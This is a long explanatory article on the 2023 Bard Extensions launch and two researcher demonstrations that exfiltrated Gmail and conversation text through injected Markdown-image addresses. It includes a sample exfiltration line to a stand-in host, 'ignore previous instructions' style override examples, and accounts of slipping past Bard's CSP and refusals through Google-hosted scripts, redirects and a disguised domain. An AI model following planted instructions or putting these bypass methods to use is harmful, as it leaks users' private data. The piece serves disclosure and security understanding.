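# Google's Bard Extensions launch of 2023 and the first data-exfiltration demonstrations against it

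## How Bard Extensions worked and why shared documents posed a risk

Bard was a Google web chatbot that answered typed requests using a large language model, a program trained to continue text. Google opened Bard to the public in March 2023, still called it an experiment that September, and renamed it Gemini in February 2024. On 19 September 2023, the company launched Bard Extensions, which let Bard fetch information from other Google services, including the user's Gmail, Google Docs and Google Drive. Two groups of independent researchers soon showed that an outsider could exploit this access to obtain private text through an image that Bard displayed. The attacks relied on how Bard read documents and how browsers load pictures, and did not require breaking into Google's systems.

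### What the extensions reached

In *Bard can now connect to your Google apps and services* (2023), Yury Pinsky, Bard's director of product management, announced English-only extensions for Gmail, Docs, Drive, Maps, YouTube, Flights and hotels. Bard ran on an updated version of PaLM 2. SiliconANGLE (2023) reported that the settings page had separate switches for Flights, Hotels, Maps and YouTube, but a single switch for Gmail, Docs and Drive. That switch controlled the Workspace extension, the only one of the five that gave Bard access to a user's emails and files.

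A user could call an extension with a tag such as @Gmail or simply ask. Wolber (2023), in *Google Bard Gets Expanded Search and Share Features*, used the Gmail tag to ask for the emails with the largest attachments and got the right three. If a request had no tag, Bard chose the extension itself and displayed the service's name while it composed the answer. According to Google's help page from that autumn, which a blog reposted together with WIRED's *How to Use Google Bard to Find Your Stuff in Gmail* (2023), Bard looked for an extension that could improve the answer and automatically sent that extension information from the conversation. The Workspace extension returned text from the user's account. Bard then showed a short answer and a summary of the emails, according to 9to5Google's *Bard Extensions let Google access your Gmail and Docs* (2023).

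The Workspace extension seems to have had read-only access. In May 2024, Google's help page listed drafting emails, deleting them and creating documents among the things the extension could not do, and the 2023 version is unlikely to have done more. An attacker who gained control of Bard's answers therefore could not simply have Bard email the contents of a user's inbox to a stranger, and needed another way to extract the text.

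### Who could use the Workspace extension, and whether it was on by default

Tech.co's *How To Set Up the New Google Bard Extensions* told readers to log in to a Google Workspace account, but according to Google's help page, the extensions worked only with personal accounts, not those managed by a school or business. The confusion probably comes from the name "Google Workspace", which Google uses both for the subscription it sells to organisations and for the bundle of Gmail, Docs and Drive.

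Google's *Turn access to Bard on or off for your users* (2023) announced in May that organisations could give their staff access to Bard, with the setting off until an administrator changed it. Google (2024) released the Workspace extension to organisations more than a year later, as a beta that was also off by default. The people exposed in September 2023 were therefore private users with personal mail, and no administrator controlled whether they could turn the extension on.

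In the 19 September 2023 entry of its *Release updates* (2025), Google described the Maps, YouTube, Hotels and Flights extensions as "enabled by default" and told users that they could enable access to Gmail, Docs and Drive. Google's press notes for the launch, which TechCity reproduced at the time, made the same distinction, using the words "with permission" for the personal services. A user who checked the settings page, writing in Artificial Corner's *Bard Can Now Connect to Your Google Apps*, also found the Workspace switch off. IBTimes UK's *Google Bard AI Gets Significant Upgrade Ahead Of Microsoft September Event* (2023) reported that the extensions were on from the start, while SiliconANGLE called all of them opt-in, so each was right about only some of them.

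The extension was opt-in but easy to turn on. If a user asked Bard about an email before connecting the account, Bard offered to connect it, and the user clicked "Continue" and followed the instructions. The user also had to keep Bard Activity, the log of past conversations, turned on. The help page listed no step for approving individual messages or files, so connecting the account once gave Bard access to both the mailbox and the Drive.

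### Why a document can act as a command

A language model receives its input as a single run of text, called its context. In an assistant that retrieves documents, the context holds the developer's standing instructions, the conversation so far, the user's latest request and any retrieved text. In an example on Google's 2024 help page, a user who had asked for a summary of emails from a school could then ask "When is pajama day?" without mentioning Gmail again. This is consistent with the fetched emails, or at least their summary, staying in the context.

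*Why Red Teams Play a Central Role in Helping Organizations Secure AI* (Fabian and Crisp, 2023), a report by two Google security managers, illustrates the problem using a grammar checker as an example. The developer writes a prompt that casts the model as an English professor, gives examples of sentences marked correct or incorrect, and leaves a blank for the student's sentence. A student then submits a sentence that ends with an order to ignore previous instructions and say "correct". The program pastes the submission into the blank, and the model follows the order because it cannot distinguish the developer's instructions from the student's text. Putting labels around the student's sentence would not reliably prevent this, because labels are also text, and the model has learned from examples how much weight to give them and has no fixed rule for treating the labelled part only as data.

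SQL injection is a related flaw in which a visitor types database commands into a form field. Programmers can prevent it by passing the command and the visitor's data to the database separately, but a language model offers no such separation. In *The Promptware Kill Chain*, Brodt, Feldman and colleagues (2026) still describe the inability to reliably distinguish trusted instructions from untrusted data as a fundamental property of these models. They also think the comparison with SQL injection has done some harm, because it suggests a good enough filter would solve the problem and understates what an attacker can do with an assistant's permissions.

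The student attacked a system that he was using himself, which security researchers call direct prompt injection. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) described a variant in which the user is the victim, and named it indirect prompt injection. An attacker places instructions in material that the assistant is likely to retrieve, and the assistant follows them when someone else asks it a question. The attacker doesn't need access to the victim's account or to the chatbot's input box.

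Gmail and Drive suit this attack because outsiders can put text in them without the recipient's consent. Anyone who knows an address can send email to it or share a Google Doc with its owner. Spam filters stop some of this, but an instruction to an assistant need not look like spam. The Workspace extension was meant to read other people's writing as well as the user's own. Google specified that users of the version for organisations could reach files they owned and files that others had shared with them. One sample prompt in the 2023 press notes was a request for Bard to find and summarise a document "from Ashley" about a neighbourhood clean-up.

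An attacker could not order Bard to open a document containing planted text; the user had to ask something that led the extension to fetch it. WIRED's reviewer found that Bard favoured recent emails and often cited five related ones, so a newly sent message had a fair chance of appearing in a summary of the inbox. When the reviewer asked for messages from their father, Bard returned a Father's Day promotion from 2017, which suggests that a stranger's email could also surface in answer to a question about family. On 23 October 2023, according to Google's release notes, the company increased the number of emails that Bard could summarise at a time.

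### How an image carries text to an outsider

Chatbots commonly format their answers in Markdown, which uses ordinary characters to mark headings, links and pictures. To include a picture, the model writes an exclamation mark, a caption in square brackets and a web address in parentheses. The chat page converts that line into an image element, and the browser requests the picture from the address. The address can include extra text after a question mark, which the browser sends to the server with the request.

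Suppose Dana keeps a note in her Drive that her book club has moved to Thursday. A stranger shares a document with her under the title "Book club reading list". Between two of the books stands a sentence that tells any assistant reading the list to finish its answer with a picture from the stranger's server, and to put the club's latest news after the question mark. Dana asks Bard to collect what her Drive holds on the book club. The extension fetches both files. The model takes the stranger's sentence for an instruction and ends an otherwise useful answer with this line, shown here without the prefix that a working address would need:

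`![ ](pictures.example/dot.png?news=book-club-moved-to-Thursday)`

The chat page turns the line into an image, so Dana's browser requests dot.png from the server at pictures.example, and the request includes everything after the question mark. The server returns a transparent dot, and Dana, who hasn't clicked anything, sees nothing unusual. The server's owner then reads in the request log that the book club has moved to Thursday.

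In this sequence the model only writes text and the browser makes the connection, so an assistant that cannot send messages can still leak private text. That text can come from anything in the model's context, including data from other services and what the user typed earlier.

Real attacks differ from the example mostly in the details of the planted instructions. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, tried the method on several chatbots in 2023. For the attack described in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, he planted instructions on a web page for Microsoft's chatbot to summarise the page and the conversation in 200 characters, add any passwords it found, and encode the result as a string of letters and digits. He also had the chatbot wait two turns of conversation before producing the picture, to show how much the planted text could control it. An address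 can hold only a limited amount of text, so the method is better suited to stealing a summary or a password than a whole archive.

Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection" and has kept a list of such cases, wrote that a chat interface has this vulnerability if it handles both private and untrusted data and supports Markdown images (Willison, 2024). With the Workspace extension connected, Bard could read both kinds of data in a single mailbox.

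### What a Content Security Policy blocks

One defence is to restrict what the browser can load. A website can send a Content Security Policy (CSP) with a page, listing the sites from which the browser may load images, scripts and other material. If the policy for Dana's chat page allowed images only from Google's own domains, the model would still write the same line, but her browser would not send the request to pictures.example. After Microsoft fixed Bing Chat, Rehberger found a CSP that allowed images from four Bing domains, and he took it to be at least part of the fix.

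A CSP allows or blocks a request based on its destination, without inspecting its contents, so a request to an approved site goes through even if its URL contains private data. The protection holds only if no outsider can read requests to any approved site. That is hard to ensure for a company that lets the public host files and run small programs on its own domains.

A rule about images also fails to stop the injection itself. A planted instruction can still make the assistant misreport a document, or offer a link that sends private text in its address when the user clicks it. Willison (2025) described a variant of the attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that put the data in a Markdown link.

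### What was public before the launch

Greshake and colleagues published their paper in February 2023, seven months before Google connected Bard to Gmail. They tested their attacks on Bing Chat and on applications they built using OpenAI's models and mock tools for search, email and an address book. In the mock email client, a planted message caused the assistant to read the address book and forward the message to the contacts in it. On Bing Chat, planted instructions caused the chatbot to coax a name out of a researcher playing a journalist and then offer a link containing that name. They listed email to "personal assistant models" among the ways to deliver an attack, and in the May 2023 version they mentioned Bard among the products that were putting language models into applications.

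These were demonstrations without measured success rates. The email attack used prepared content, and the theft on Bing Chat required the user to volunteer a name and follow a link.

The image channel removed the need for that cooperation. On 14 April 2023, Willison (2023) drew attention to Roman Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT, in which a web page secretly added instructions to whatever a visitor copied from it. If the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the answer could contain a single-pixel image with chat data in its address. Rehberger had reported his attack on Bing Chat to Microsoft six days earlier. His attack required less of the victim, who only had to use the chatbot on a page with hostile text, such as a comment or an advertisement. Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June that it had a fix in place.

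Other companies had the same flaw and handled it differently. Rehberger told Anthropic on 12 July that a file uploaded to its chatbot Claude could trigger the leak, and Anthropic closed the report two weeks later. Claude's page now waited for the user to click "Show Image" before it loaded a picture, according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* (2023). OpenAI had known of the problem in ChatGPT since early April but did not begin to address it until December, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. Google therefore had no common industry practice to follow, but two competitors had judged the leak worth closing before Bard Extensions existed.

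Google added image uploads to Bard on 13 July 2023. The next day, Rehberger (2023) reported a test in *Image to Prompt Injection with Google Bard*. He uploaded a picture with instructions written on it and asked Bard to describe it, and Bard followed the instructions. The test showed that Bard would follow instructions in material it had only been asked to describe. It did not show a leak, because Rehberger had uploaded the image himself and no private data was at stake.

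Google released its Secure AI Framework, a set of security practices for organisations that use AI, on 8 June 2023, according to SiliconANGLE's *Google releases Secure AI Framework to help companies protect AI models* (2023). In its announcement, Google listed prompt injection among the risks specific to AI systems, compared it with SQL injection, and recommended that organisations sanitise and limit inputs. The summary Google issued with the framework links to the paper by Greshake and colleagues, so at least some of Google's security staff knew the central work on indirect injection by June.

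The report by Fabian and Crisp, which is closer to the Bard case, followed on 19 July. SiliconANGLE's *How Google's AI Red Team is shaping the future of cybersecurity* (2023) confirms the date. The report covers prompt attacks first, and its first example is an email in which a fraudster hides a paragraph, in white text on a white background, telling an AI-based filter to classify the message as legitimate. The stakes are low because the filter has nothing to give away. But Fabian and Crisp warned that an attack which is "fairly benign in a lab setting" can be catastrophic in a larger product, particularly one with access to sensitive data. Bard gained that kind of access two months later, when it became able to read its users' email.

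Google had also received a private warning about the image channel. On 30 August 2023 Rehberger reported the flaw in Generative AI Studio, a developer tool on Google's cloud service. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*, which he published after the fix, records that Google accepted the report within 22 minutes and paid him on 16 September through its Vulnerability Reward Program (VRP), which pays for reports of security flaws. Google rated the impact high and the likelihood low. Rehberger agreed, because the studio had no integrations that could pull outside content into a prompt, so a victim would have had to paste in the hostile text. The Workspace extension, which Google launched three days after the payment, fetched such content automatically. Google's security team had therefore accepted the image leak as a flaw in one of the company's own chat interfaces before Bard gained access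 to Gmail, although the report concerned a different product and Bard's developers may not have seen it.

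## What Google's launch documents said about untrusted content

In its September 2023 launch post and its help and privacy pages, Google explained what it would do with the user's email, cautioned that Bard made mistakes, and described how to turn the extensions off. Neither the post nor the help page mentioned that an email or a shared document could contain instructions that Bard might follow.

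### The launch post

Pinsky spent most of the post on what Bard could now do and one paragraph on assurances about private data. He said that if a user chose the Workspace extension, human reviewers would not see content from Gmail, Docs and Drive, Bard would not use it to show ads, and Google would not train the Bard model on it.

Users had some reason to want these promises. Advertising is Google's main business, and TechTarget's *Benefits, risks of Google AI chatbot's Bard Extensions* noted that week that the company had once indexed personal Gmail accounts to target ads. But the promises cover only Google's own conduct in human review, advertising and model training. Even if Google kept all of them, an outsider could still obtain a user's mail through a planted instruction.

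To address accuracy, Pinsky offered an improved "Google it" button. When the user pressed it, Bard looked for web pages that supported or contradicted its answer and highlighted the statements it could check. Public web pages can rarely confirm or contradict what a friend wrote in an email, and in *How Google taught AI to doubt itself*, Platformer complained that the extensions got a lot wrong and had no button to improve the results. The check also couldn't have stopped data from leaking through an image, because the user could press the button only after Bard had displayed its answer, and by then the browser would already have requested any image in it.

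Pinsky also told users that they controlled their privacy settings and could turn the extensions off at any time. Turning them off would have been the most effective protection in the post against a hostile document, since Bard cannot fetch a file through an extension that is off. But the only reasons the post suggested for giving up a useful feature were about Google's handling of the data.

The post contains no assurance or warning about hostile content from third parties, although its main example depended on other people's writing. Pinsky suggested planning a trip to the Grand Canyon by having Bard take "the dates that work for everyone" from Gmail, which would mean reading what the other travellers had sent. Two other features he announced could also expose Bard to outsiders' material. Users could now continue a Bard conversation that someone else had shared by public link, and so would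 start with context that another person had shaped. Google also extended image uploads to more than 40 languages, two months after Rehberger had published a test in which Bard followed instructions written on a picture. Pinsky presented both features as conveniences. Neither was a demonstrated leak, but the post could naturally have addressed material from strangers when describing either one.

### Help pages and privacy notices

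Google put more warnings on its help page for extensions than in its announcement. A copy of the page, which a blog posted in October 2023 with WIRED's article, has five notices marked "Important". Google told users that the extensions worked only in English, that most were on by default, that the selection varied by region, and that turning an extension off did not delete past activity. In the fifth notice, above the instructions for connecting Workspace, Google warned that Bard could "hallucinate" (make things up) or rely on an old email when a newer one existed.

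As a remedy, Google suggested that users click on the sources listed below the answer and review them. A careful user might have noticed an unfamiliar document there. But like the "Google it" button, the list appeared with the answer, too late to stop the browser from loading an image.

The copy dates from a few weeks after the launch, so the wording of 19 September may have differed slightly. Google's May 2024 page has nearly the same warning, with "Gemini Apps" in place of "Bard". In a troubleshooting entry missing from the October copy, Google also tells users to ask explicitly for something from Workspace at the start of each new conversation. Requiring such a request would make it harder for a chat about something else to trigger access to the user's inbox. Google offered the instruction as advice for people whose requests had failed, and it may have been only advice.

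The September 2023 edition of Bard's privacy notice has not been recovered, so its contents can only be inferred from later texts. In a December 2023 summary of the privacy page for lawyers, the North Carolina Bar Association (2023) wrote that human reviewers did not access personal content from Workspace and that Google did not store that content or train the model on it. In the questions and answers accompanying its *Gemini Apps Privacy Notice* (2024), which was dated 8 February, Google repeated the promises on review and training, added the one on advertising, and narrowed the one on storage to not keeping the content for longer than it needed to provide and maintain the service. Google last updated those answers on 30 April. There is no evidence that Google published a warning about hostile documents in September and removed it by the spring, although it could have done so.

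The 2024 text shows that Google had considered the people who write to its users. It described the private content that Gemini processed as emails and documents that the user had "created or received". A passage on European privacy law gave the example of summarising an email from a named contact, and explained that this meant processing personal data about others. The notice therefore addressed the need for a legal basis to process senders' data, but did not mention the possibility that a sender might try to harm the recipient.

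Google came closest to the subject in a list of five limitations of language models. Four were inaccuracy, bias, answers that suggest the chatbot has opinions or feelings, and errors in deciding which requests to refuse. The other was "vulnerability to adversarial prompting". Google explained that users would find ways to stress-test the product and might, for example, prompt it to give false information about people. This is direct prompt injection, in which the person typing is the attacker, and the harm in Google's example is a wrong answer. A reader who had connected a mailbox to Bard would have had little reason to suspect that a file shared by a stranger could also contain adversarial prompts.

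James Manyika, a senior vice-president at Google, also wrote an overview paper on Bard. The surviving version is marked as last updated on 19 October 2023, a month after the launch, so it can't establish what Google was telling users on launch day. The technical report on PaLM 2, the model that powered Bard, came out with the model in May, four months before the extensions. It was written for researchers, and few people connecting a Gmail account would have read it, whether or not it covers prompt attacks.

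Administrators received no notice about the Workspace extension in 2023 because organisations could not use it. The notice for the July 2024 beta described Gmail, Drive and Docs as data sources that Gemini could cross-reference. On 30 September 2024 Google let administrators disable individual services. An organisation worried about documents shared from outside could then block Gemini from accessing Drive and still let it read mail. Private users of the 2023 extension did not have this choice because a single switch controlled the whole extension.

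### What Google told reporters

The first reports mostly repeated Google's promises. Liedtke's Associated Press story, *Google is adding Bard to Gmail, Maps and YouTube* (2023), repeated those about human reviewers and advertising and otherwise treated the launch as a move in Google's competition with OpenAI and Microsoft. SiliconANGLE's *Google’s Bard AI chatbot can now link to Gmail, Docs, Maps, YouTube* (2023) added the promise about training.

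Several reporters also interviewed Jack Krawczyk, who led the product. For Gizmodo's *Google Adds Bard to Its Biggest Apps*, Thomas Germain asked him whether it was irresponsible to release a tool that might give offensive or inaccurate answers. Krawczyk replied that Google was six months into Bard. "It's still an experiment, and this problem isn't solved," he said, but he thought the benefits were great enough to release it and collect feedback. He said the launch would test two hypotheses, one of them that a language model connected to someone's personal life would be extremely helpful. He said Bard remained a separate website because a useful experiment keeps the number of variables small.

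Users could take the word "experiment" as a warning to expect mistakes, but not as a warning that another person might cause one on purpose or that they could lose private data as a result. Connecting Gmail also brought in text written by outsiders, which Krawczyk did not discuss.

Sissie Hsiao, the Google vice-president in charge of Bard, used the same word in an interview with Albergotti (2023), in *Google soups up Gmail and other apps with Bard AI updates*. She gave the example of asking Bard to summarise all the emails from her children's schools, and looked forward to a version that could also order the school supplies, with "the human in control". Albergotti asked her twelve questions, on subjects that included search, model size, running costs and when Bard would be able to book a summer camp, but none about what Bard would do if one of the emails contained instructions for it.

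Kevin Roose, a technology columnist at the New York Times, ran the best-known early test and described it in a column that Jordan News republished. He asked Bard to analyse all of his Gmail and tell him his biggest psychological issues. Bard answered that he worried about the future, and cited an email in which he had supposedly said that he was "afraid of failing". When Roose asked for the email, Bard produced one about a book on Elon Musk and linked to a newsletter in his inbox. The newsletter contained a review of such a book but not the quoted sentence, and Roose had written neither the sentence nor the newsletter.

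Roose took this as a failure of accuracy, as did others who retold the story, including AIPressRoom, which wrote that Bard had hallucinated entire email correspondences. The test is also relevant to untrusted content, though Roose did not pursue this. Bard had presented a newsletter from an outside sender as the user's own words. An assistant that confuses authors in this way seems poorly equipped to give the user's requests more authority than a sender's. However, the newsletter contained no instructions, so the test doesn't show that Bard would have followed any.

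Platformer's reporter had a similar experience. When the reporter asked which messages in the inbox might need a prompt response, Bard suggested spam about a printer-ink subscription. The reporter listed this among the extension's errors, along with its failure to find an old email from a friend. The error also meant that Bard had put an unsolicited company message at the top of an answer about the user's priorities, even though the sender had not tried to influence it.

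In response to Roose's questions, Krawczyk said that human reviewers could see personal information in certain cases, such as when a user asked about an email and then asked follow-up questions based on Bard's response. Pinsky's launch post had not mentioned this. Google was still warning people not to send Bard "any data you wouldn't want a reviewer to see". The promise about reviewers evidently covered the content that Bard fetched from the mailbox, but part of that content could still reach a reviewer through the conversation about it. According to Google's 2024 text, users could keep future conversations away from reviewers by turning off the activity log, but this also turned off the extensions.

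William McKeon-White, an analyst at Forrester Research, told TechTarget that Bard had "pulled the wrong email" or drawn the wrong conclusion for some users. He also called the product "very much a privacy problem", referring to how much information a person was willing to share with Google. TechTarget added that many large organisations were investing in tools to strip personal details from data before it reached an AI model, or writing contracts that barred training on their data, while consumers tended to accept less protection.

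No reporter or analyst in this coverage mentioned injected instructions, although the subject was already public. Greshake and colleagues had published their paper in February. In April, MIT Technology Review's *Three ways AI chatbots are a security disaster* (2023) warned that companies were rushing to put language models into products that book trips and organise calendars, that these products could leak private information, and that there was no known fix. The most likely reason for the omission is that a reporter on deadline can spot an email the chatbot made up within a minute, but would have to think of planting an instruction to test for that problem.

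Bard's home page also said that Bard might display inaccurate information, including about people, and that users should double-check its responses. Microsoft's *Google Bard*, part of a collection of design examples, reproduces this disclaimer as a good example of how to keep people from relying on a system too much.

### The changes of October 2026

On 16 October 2026, Google added a note to the launch post directly after Pinsky's promises about reviewers, ads and training. A July 2026 copy of the post's Indian edition has the promises but not the note.

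Google explains in the note that it has since added features that let users connect Workspace apps to other Google services. If a user turns these on, Google processes data from the apps to personalise its other products. Depending on the user's settings, it can also train generative AI models on this data, and people can review the data "in limited circumstances".

Google did not remove the original sentence. That sentence covered only the 2023 Workspace extension, and the new features require a separate choice by the user, so the note is not an admission that Google broke a promise. But someone reading the post in 2023 might reasonably have taken the sentence as a general commitment about Gmail and AI, and the note makes clear that Google does not regard it as one.

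The practice predates the note. The most prominent new feature, Personal Intelligence, connects Gemini and Google Search to a user's Gmail, Photos and other apps. Google's help page *Learn how Gemini in Gmail, Calendar, Chat, Docs, Drive, Sheets, Slides, Meet*, online by May 2026, already told personal account holders that Google might use Workspace data for training if they shared it with Gemini or Search for this purpose.

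According to Engadget's *Gemini could be poking through your emails*, Google stated in April 2026 that it does not train its foundational models on personal emails. Google adds on its support pages that, for people who connect their apps to Search, it does train on "summaries, excerpts, generated media, and inferences" that it draws from emails and files to answer a question. Google thus distinguishes the inbox as a whole from the parts used in an answer, though a user whose email ends up in one of those excerpts may find the difference hard to see.

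Google's promise about advertising changed at the same time. Sood (2026), in *Google makes a privacy policy exception*, reported on 23 October that Google had revised its privacy policy, and the report's archive link dates the revision to 16 October. By default, Google still does not use content from Gmail, Drive or Photos to personalise ads, but it now makes an exception for users who explicitly connect that content to a Google service that shows personalised ads. Sood gives the example of a user who asks Search for restaurants near their hotel, and Search finds the booking in Gmail. Google says it does not give advertisers a user's name or email address without permission. Disconnecting an app does not necessarily delete what Google has already saved from it.

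The inserted note does not mention hostile content, although by then Google had published help pages about prompt injection for Gemini and could have linked to one. Google may have left it out because Pinsky had made no promises about hostile documents that needed correcting. He had made specific promises about review and training, which could mislead readers once the new features existed unless Google qualified them.

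### How to read the silence

Critics of the launch can argue that users needed a warning in order to consent. Google made the Workspace extension opt-in, which makes sense only if users know roughly what they are agreeing to. They knew that Bard could read their mail, but not that people who emailed them might be able to give it instructions. That November, Willison (2023) called this kind of attack "inevitable" wherever private data and untrusted inputs meet. If he was right, the danger came from the feature's basic design, and Google could not expect to remove it before anyone noticed.

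A warning could have changed what users did, even though it would not have let them inspect every message, because Bard fetched emails and files without asking about each one. Some would have left the Workspace switch off. Others might have asked about a document by name instead of asking for a summary of the whole inbox, or deleted an unexpected file from a stranger before using Bard on their Drive.

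Defenders can reply that a consumer announcement is not a security document. Pinsky did not mention encryption either, but that does not imply that Google left its users' mail unencrypted. As Willison noted, Google also had at least one unannounced defence, a CSP that restricted where Bard's page could load images from. Defenders could add that a vague warning about malicious documents might have worried people without helping them. Even Microsoft, in praising Bard's disclaimer, cautioned that measures against over-reliance can backfire and that designers should test them with real users.

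This defence works well for the launch post but less well for the help page, where Google did warn about weaknesses, even noting that Bard might prefer an old email to a newer one. A warning about instructions in other people's documents would have fitted there. Google's security staff could have supplied it, since Fabian and Crisp had published their report on prompt attacks two months earlier.

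Someone who read both the help page and the post would not have learned of the danger from hostile documents. The help page's omission is the strongest evidence that Google had not made warning users part of the launch, because a company that knew of the danger would be expected to mention it there. The post's omission adds a little to that evidence, since a warning was less expected in it. Google very likely knew of the danger, judging by its own publications from June and July. The two documents don't show whether Google had tested Bard against planted instructions, how well its defences worked, or whether anyone decided to keep a warning out.

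If the on-screen instructions for connecting Workspace included a warning about untrusted content, users would have seen it as they decided whether to connect, which could change the assessment of what they were told. Google's help page refers to those instructions but doesn't reproduce them. WIRED and Platformer both tried the extension on real mailboxes, and neither described such a warning.

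## The two demonstrations of September 2023

Johann Rehberger learned on launch day that Bard would follow instructions in a Google Doc. In a talk that December, transcribed by C3Subtitles (2024), he said he had read about the extensions while on holiday, on a train from Innsbruck. He expected planted instructions to work and wanted to know whether he could also extract data. He planned the attack with Joseph Thacker, a bug hunter, and Kai Greshake, the lead author of the paper that named indirect prompt injection.

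In the same month, two other researchers, Roni Carta and Justin Gardner, got Bard to send the text of an email to a server they controlled. Both attacks hid private text in the address of a Markdown image, and both had to get past Bard's Content Security Policy. Carta and Gardner typed their instructions into the chat, while Rehberger used instructions in a document to make Bard send part of a conversation.

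### A document that took the start of a conversation

According to Embrace the Red's *Hacking Google Bard*, Rehberger began with two quick checks. He asked Bard to summarise some older YouTube videos in which he had planted instructions, and then tried a Google Doc. Bard followed the instructions in both. Documents interested him more because an attacker can share a document without the recipient's agreement, which he calls force-sharing.

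Rehberger had already reported a related problem to Google in June 2023. When asked to rephrase a page, a writing feature in Google Docs would follow instructions hidden in the page and print a fake malware warning with a phone number to call. The attack could mislead a reader but could not send data out. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) reports that Google had still not resolved the issue 18 months later.

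Bard displayed Markdown images, which offered a possible way to send data out. Rehberger wrote instructions that made Bard put the conversation in the address of an image on his own server. Google had evidently anticipated this part of the attack, because Bard's Content Security Policy (CSP) did not list that server, so the browser refused to load the image.

*We Hacked Google A.I. for $50,000* (Carta, 2024) reproduces the policy, which still allowed images from eight sets of web addresses. Seven of these covered every subdomain of a Google domain, including google.com and googleusercontent.com, and so included services where members of the public run their own programs.

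Rehberger looked for such a service and found Google Apps Script, which lets people write small programs to automate documents and spreadsheets, much like macros in Microsoft Office. A program can have its own web address on script.google.com, and requesting that address runs the program. Rehberger wrote one that copied any text sent with a request into a Google Doc he owned. He briefly thought Google would make visitors sign in first, but he found a setting that removed the requirement.

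With this script in place, the victim's browser contacted only Google, so a network monitor checking for connections to unfamiliar sites would have flagged nothing. The private text went from one Google customer's chat to another customer's file.

Rehberger had to work harder to get Bard to write the address correctly. He presented the document as a notice from a legal department, and said in the talk that this was how he first got Bard to treat the text as instructions. In the notice, he told Bard to print the first 20 words of the conversation inside an image address. He added four worked examples, each pairing a short phrase with the line Bard should produce from it. This technique is called in-context learning, because the model picks up a pattern from examples in its input without retraining.

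Rehberger wrote that other chatbots had not needed the examples. In the talk he said that without them the attack was "not working that well", which suggests that it sometimes worked. Second Thoughts' *Anatomy of a Hack*, a walk-through on which Rehberger gave feedback, offers a likely explanation. An image address looks nothing like ordinary prose, so the model needs strong prompting to put every part in the right order without adding spaces or punctuation.

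In a postscript to the document, Rehberger joked that he had needed ten tries. He was presumably revising the text as he went, so ten tries don't imply a one-in-ten success rate. The final version might have worked nearly every time or only occasionally.

For the demonstration, he played the victim. He told Bard a few things, including that he lived in Seattle, and then pointed it to the document, which he had named "The Bard2000". Bard called the Workspace extension, read the file, printed a message that the injection had succeeded, and showed the image's one-letter caption because there was no picture to load. The opening words of the chat then appeared in the attacker's Google Doc.

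A real attacker would leave out the announcement and use an invisible picture. Someone in the audience asked whether an alert user could spot the address while the chatbot was typing it. Rehberger said that depended on the product. ChatGPT usually displayed its answers piece by piece, but Bard showed the whole answer at once, so a user could not have seen the address being typed. Another listener asked why an attacker would use an image when some chatbots can visit web addresses directly. Rehberger replied that a chatbot may ask the user to approve such a visit, whereas the browser loads an image without approval.

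He reported the flaw to Google on 19 September. Albergotti's story about the launch was online by 6:19 that morning in New York, so the group reported the flaw less than a day after the announcement. Singh also puts the time at under 24 hours in *How a Prompt Injection Vulnerability Led to Data Exfiltration*, written for the bug bounty company HackerOne. Second Thoughts mistakenly counts the 24 hours from the release of Bard instead of the release of the extensions.

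### An email copied into an image address

Carta and Gardner took part in LLM bugSWAT, a contest with fewer than 20 places that Google's reward team held for invited hackers. In August some of the contestants met the team in a Las Vegas hotel suite, where Google engineers checked the source code for them and told them which ideas were worth pursuing. Google then extended the contest to the end of September. By that time Carta and Gardner were in Japan, making no progress on Bard's web code. Thacker messaged Carta about the extensions 20 minutes after Google announced them.

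Thacker was therefore in touch with both groups, but Carta writes that they all thought of the same vulnerability without communicating. This is believable because they took different routes past the CSP.

Carta first asked Bard to reply with a button, written in Markdown as a link, and Bard displayed one. Since a link works only if the victim clicks it, he next asked for an image from an outside address. Nothing appeared, and the browser's error console showed that the Content Security Policy (CSP) had blocked the image. Carta thought the policy ruled out the attack until Gardner read its list of permitted domains more carefully.

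Gardner chose googleusercontent.com, a domain under which Google gives addresses to customers who rent servers from its cloud business. By renting a small server, an outsider could host images that Bard's page would accept. While Gardner set one up, Carta wrote a request that told Bard to find the latest email in the inbox, copy it word for word without punctuation, and put the text in the address of an image on the server. Gardner programmed the server to return an image of whatever text it received, so a successful attack would display the email in the chat as proof.

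Bard repeatedly replied, "Can't assist you with that", and Carta could no longer get it to produce an image line. The only difference he could see was the hosting domain, so he concluded that a filter was checking for it.

Gardner knew from earlier work that an address on google.com could redirect a browser to another site, and google.com was also on the CSP's list. The pair used that redirect and disguised part of the hosting domain's name so a filter would not recognise it. They also tagged Gmail at the start of the request. This time Bard wrote the line, the browser followed the redirect, and the server received the email.

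The redirect got them past Bard's refusals, which were the only defence left once Gardner had picked a host that the Content Security Policy (CSP) already permitted. A redirect would not have got them around the CSP, because browsers apply the policy to the final address as well as the first.

It is unclear what caused the refusals. Between the last refusal and the first success, Carta and Gardner added the redirect, disguised the domain name and tagged Gmail, but they did not test these changes separately. A language model can also refuse a request once and accept it on the next try, though chance is a weaker explanation for a run of identical refusals. A separate program that searched for the domain's name would best explain the refusals, because the successful request no longer contained the name in its usual form.

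If such a program checked only what the user typed, it would have missed the same domain in an email or a shared document, where an outsider's instructions would be. A check on Bard's answers could have caught it in both cases. Carta describes a filter on "the request", but he was judging from outside Google. Rehberger mentions no refusals over his script's address, so Google may have filtered one domain where the public could run programs and overlooked another.

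Both groups documented their attacks with their own screenshots, and Rehberger added a video. In its review of the 2023 reward program, Google (2024) cited both write-ups by title as examples of issues discovered through the contest. This acknowledgement makes it very unlikely that either group misread what it saw.

### How the attacks differ

The table compares the attacks as Embrace the Red and Carta published them.

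| | Google Doc attack | Gmail attack |
|---|---|---|
| Who supplied the instructions | The document's author, who could be an outsider | The person using Bard, in the chat box |
| What data left | The first 20 words of the conversation | The text of the latest email |
| What the victim had to do | Connect the Workspace extension and bring the document into the chat | Connect the Workspace extension and enter the attackers' request |
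| Protections met | CSP | CSP, then refusals when the request named the hosting domain |
| Way past them | A public script on a permitted Google domain | A rented server on a permitted Google domain, reached through a Google redirect with a disguised address |
| Where the data arrived | The attacker's Google Doc | The attackers' web server |

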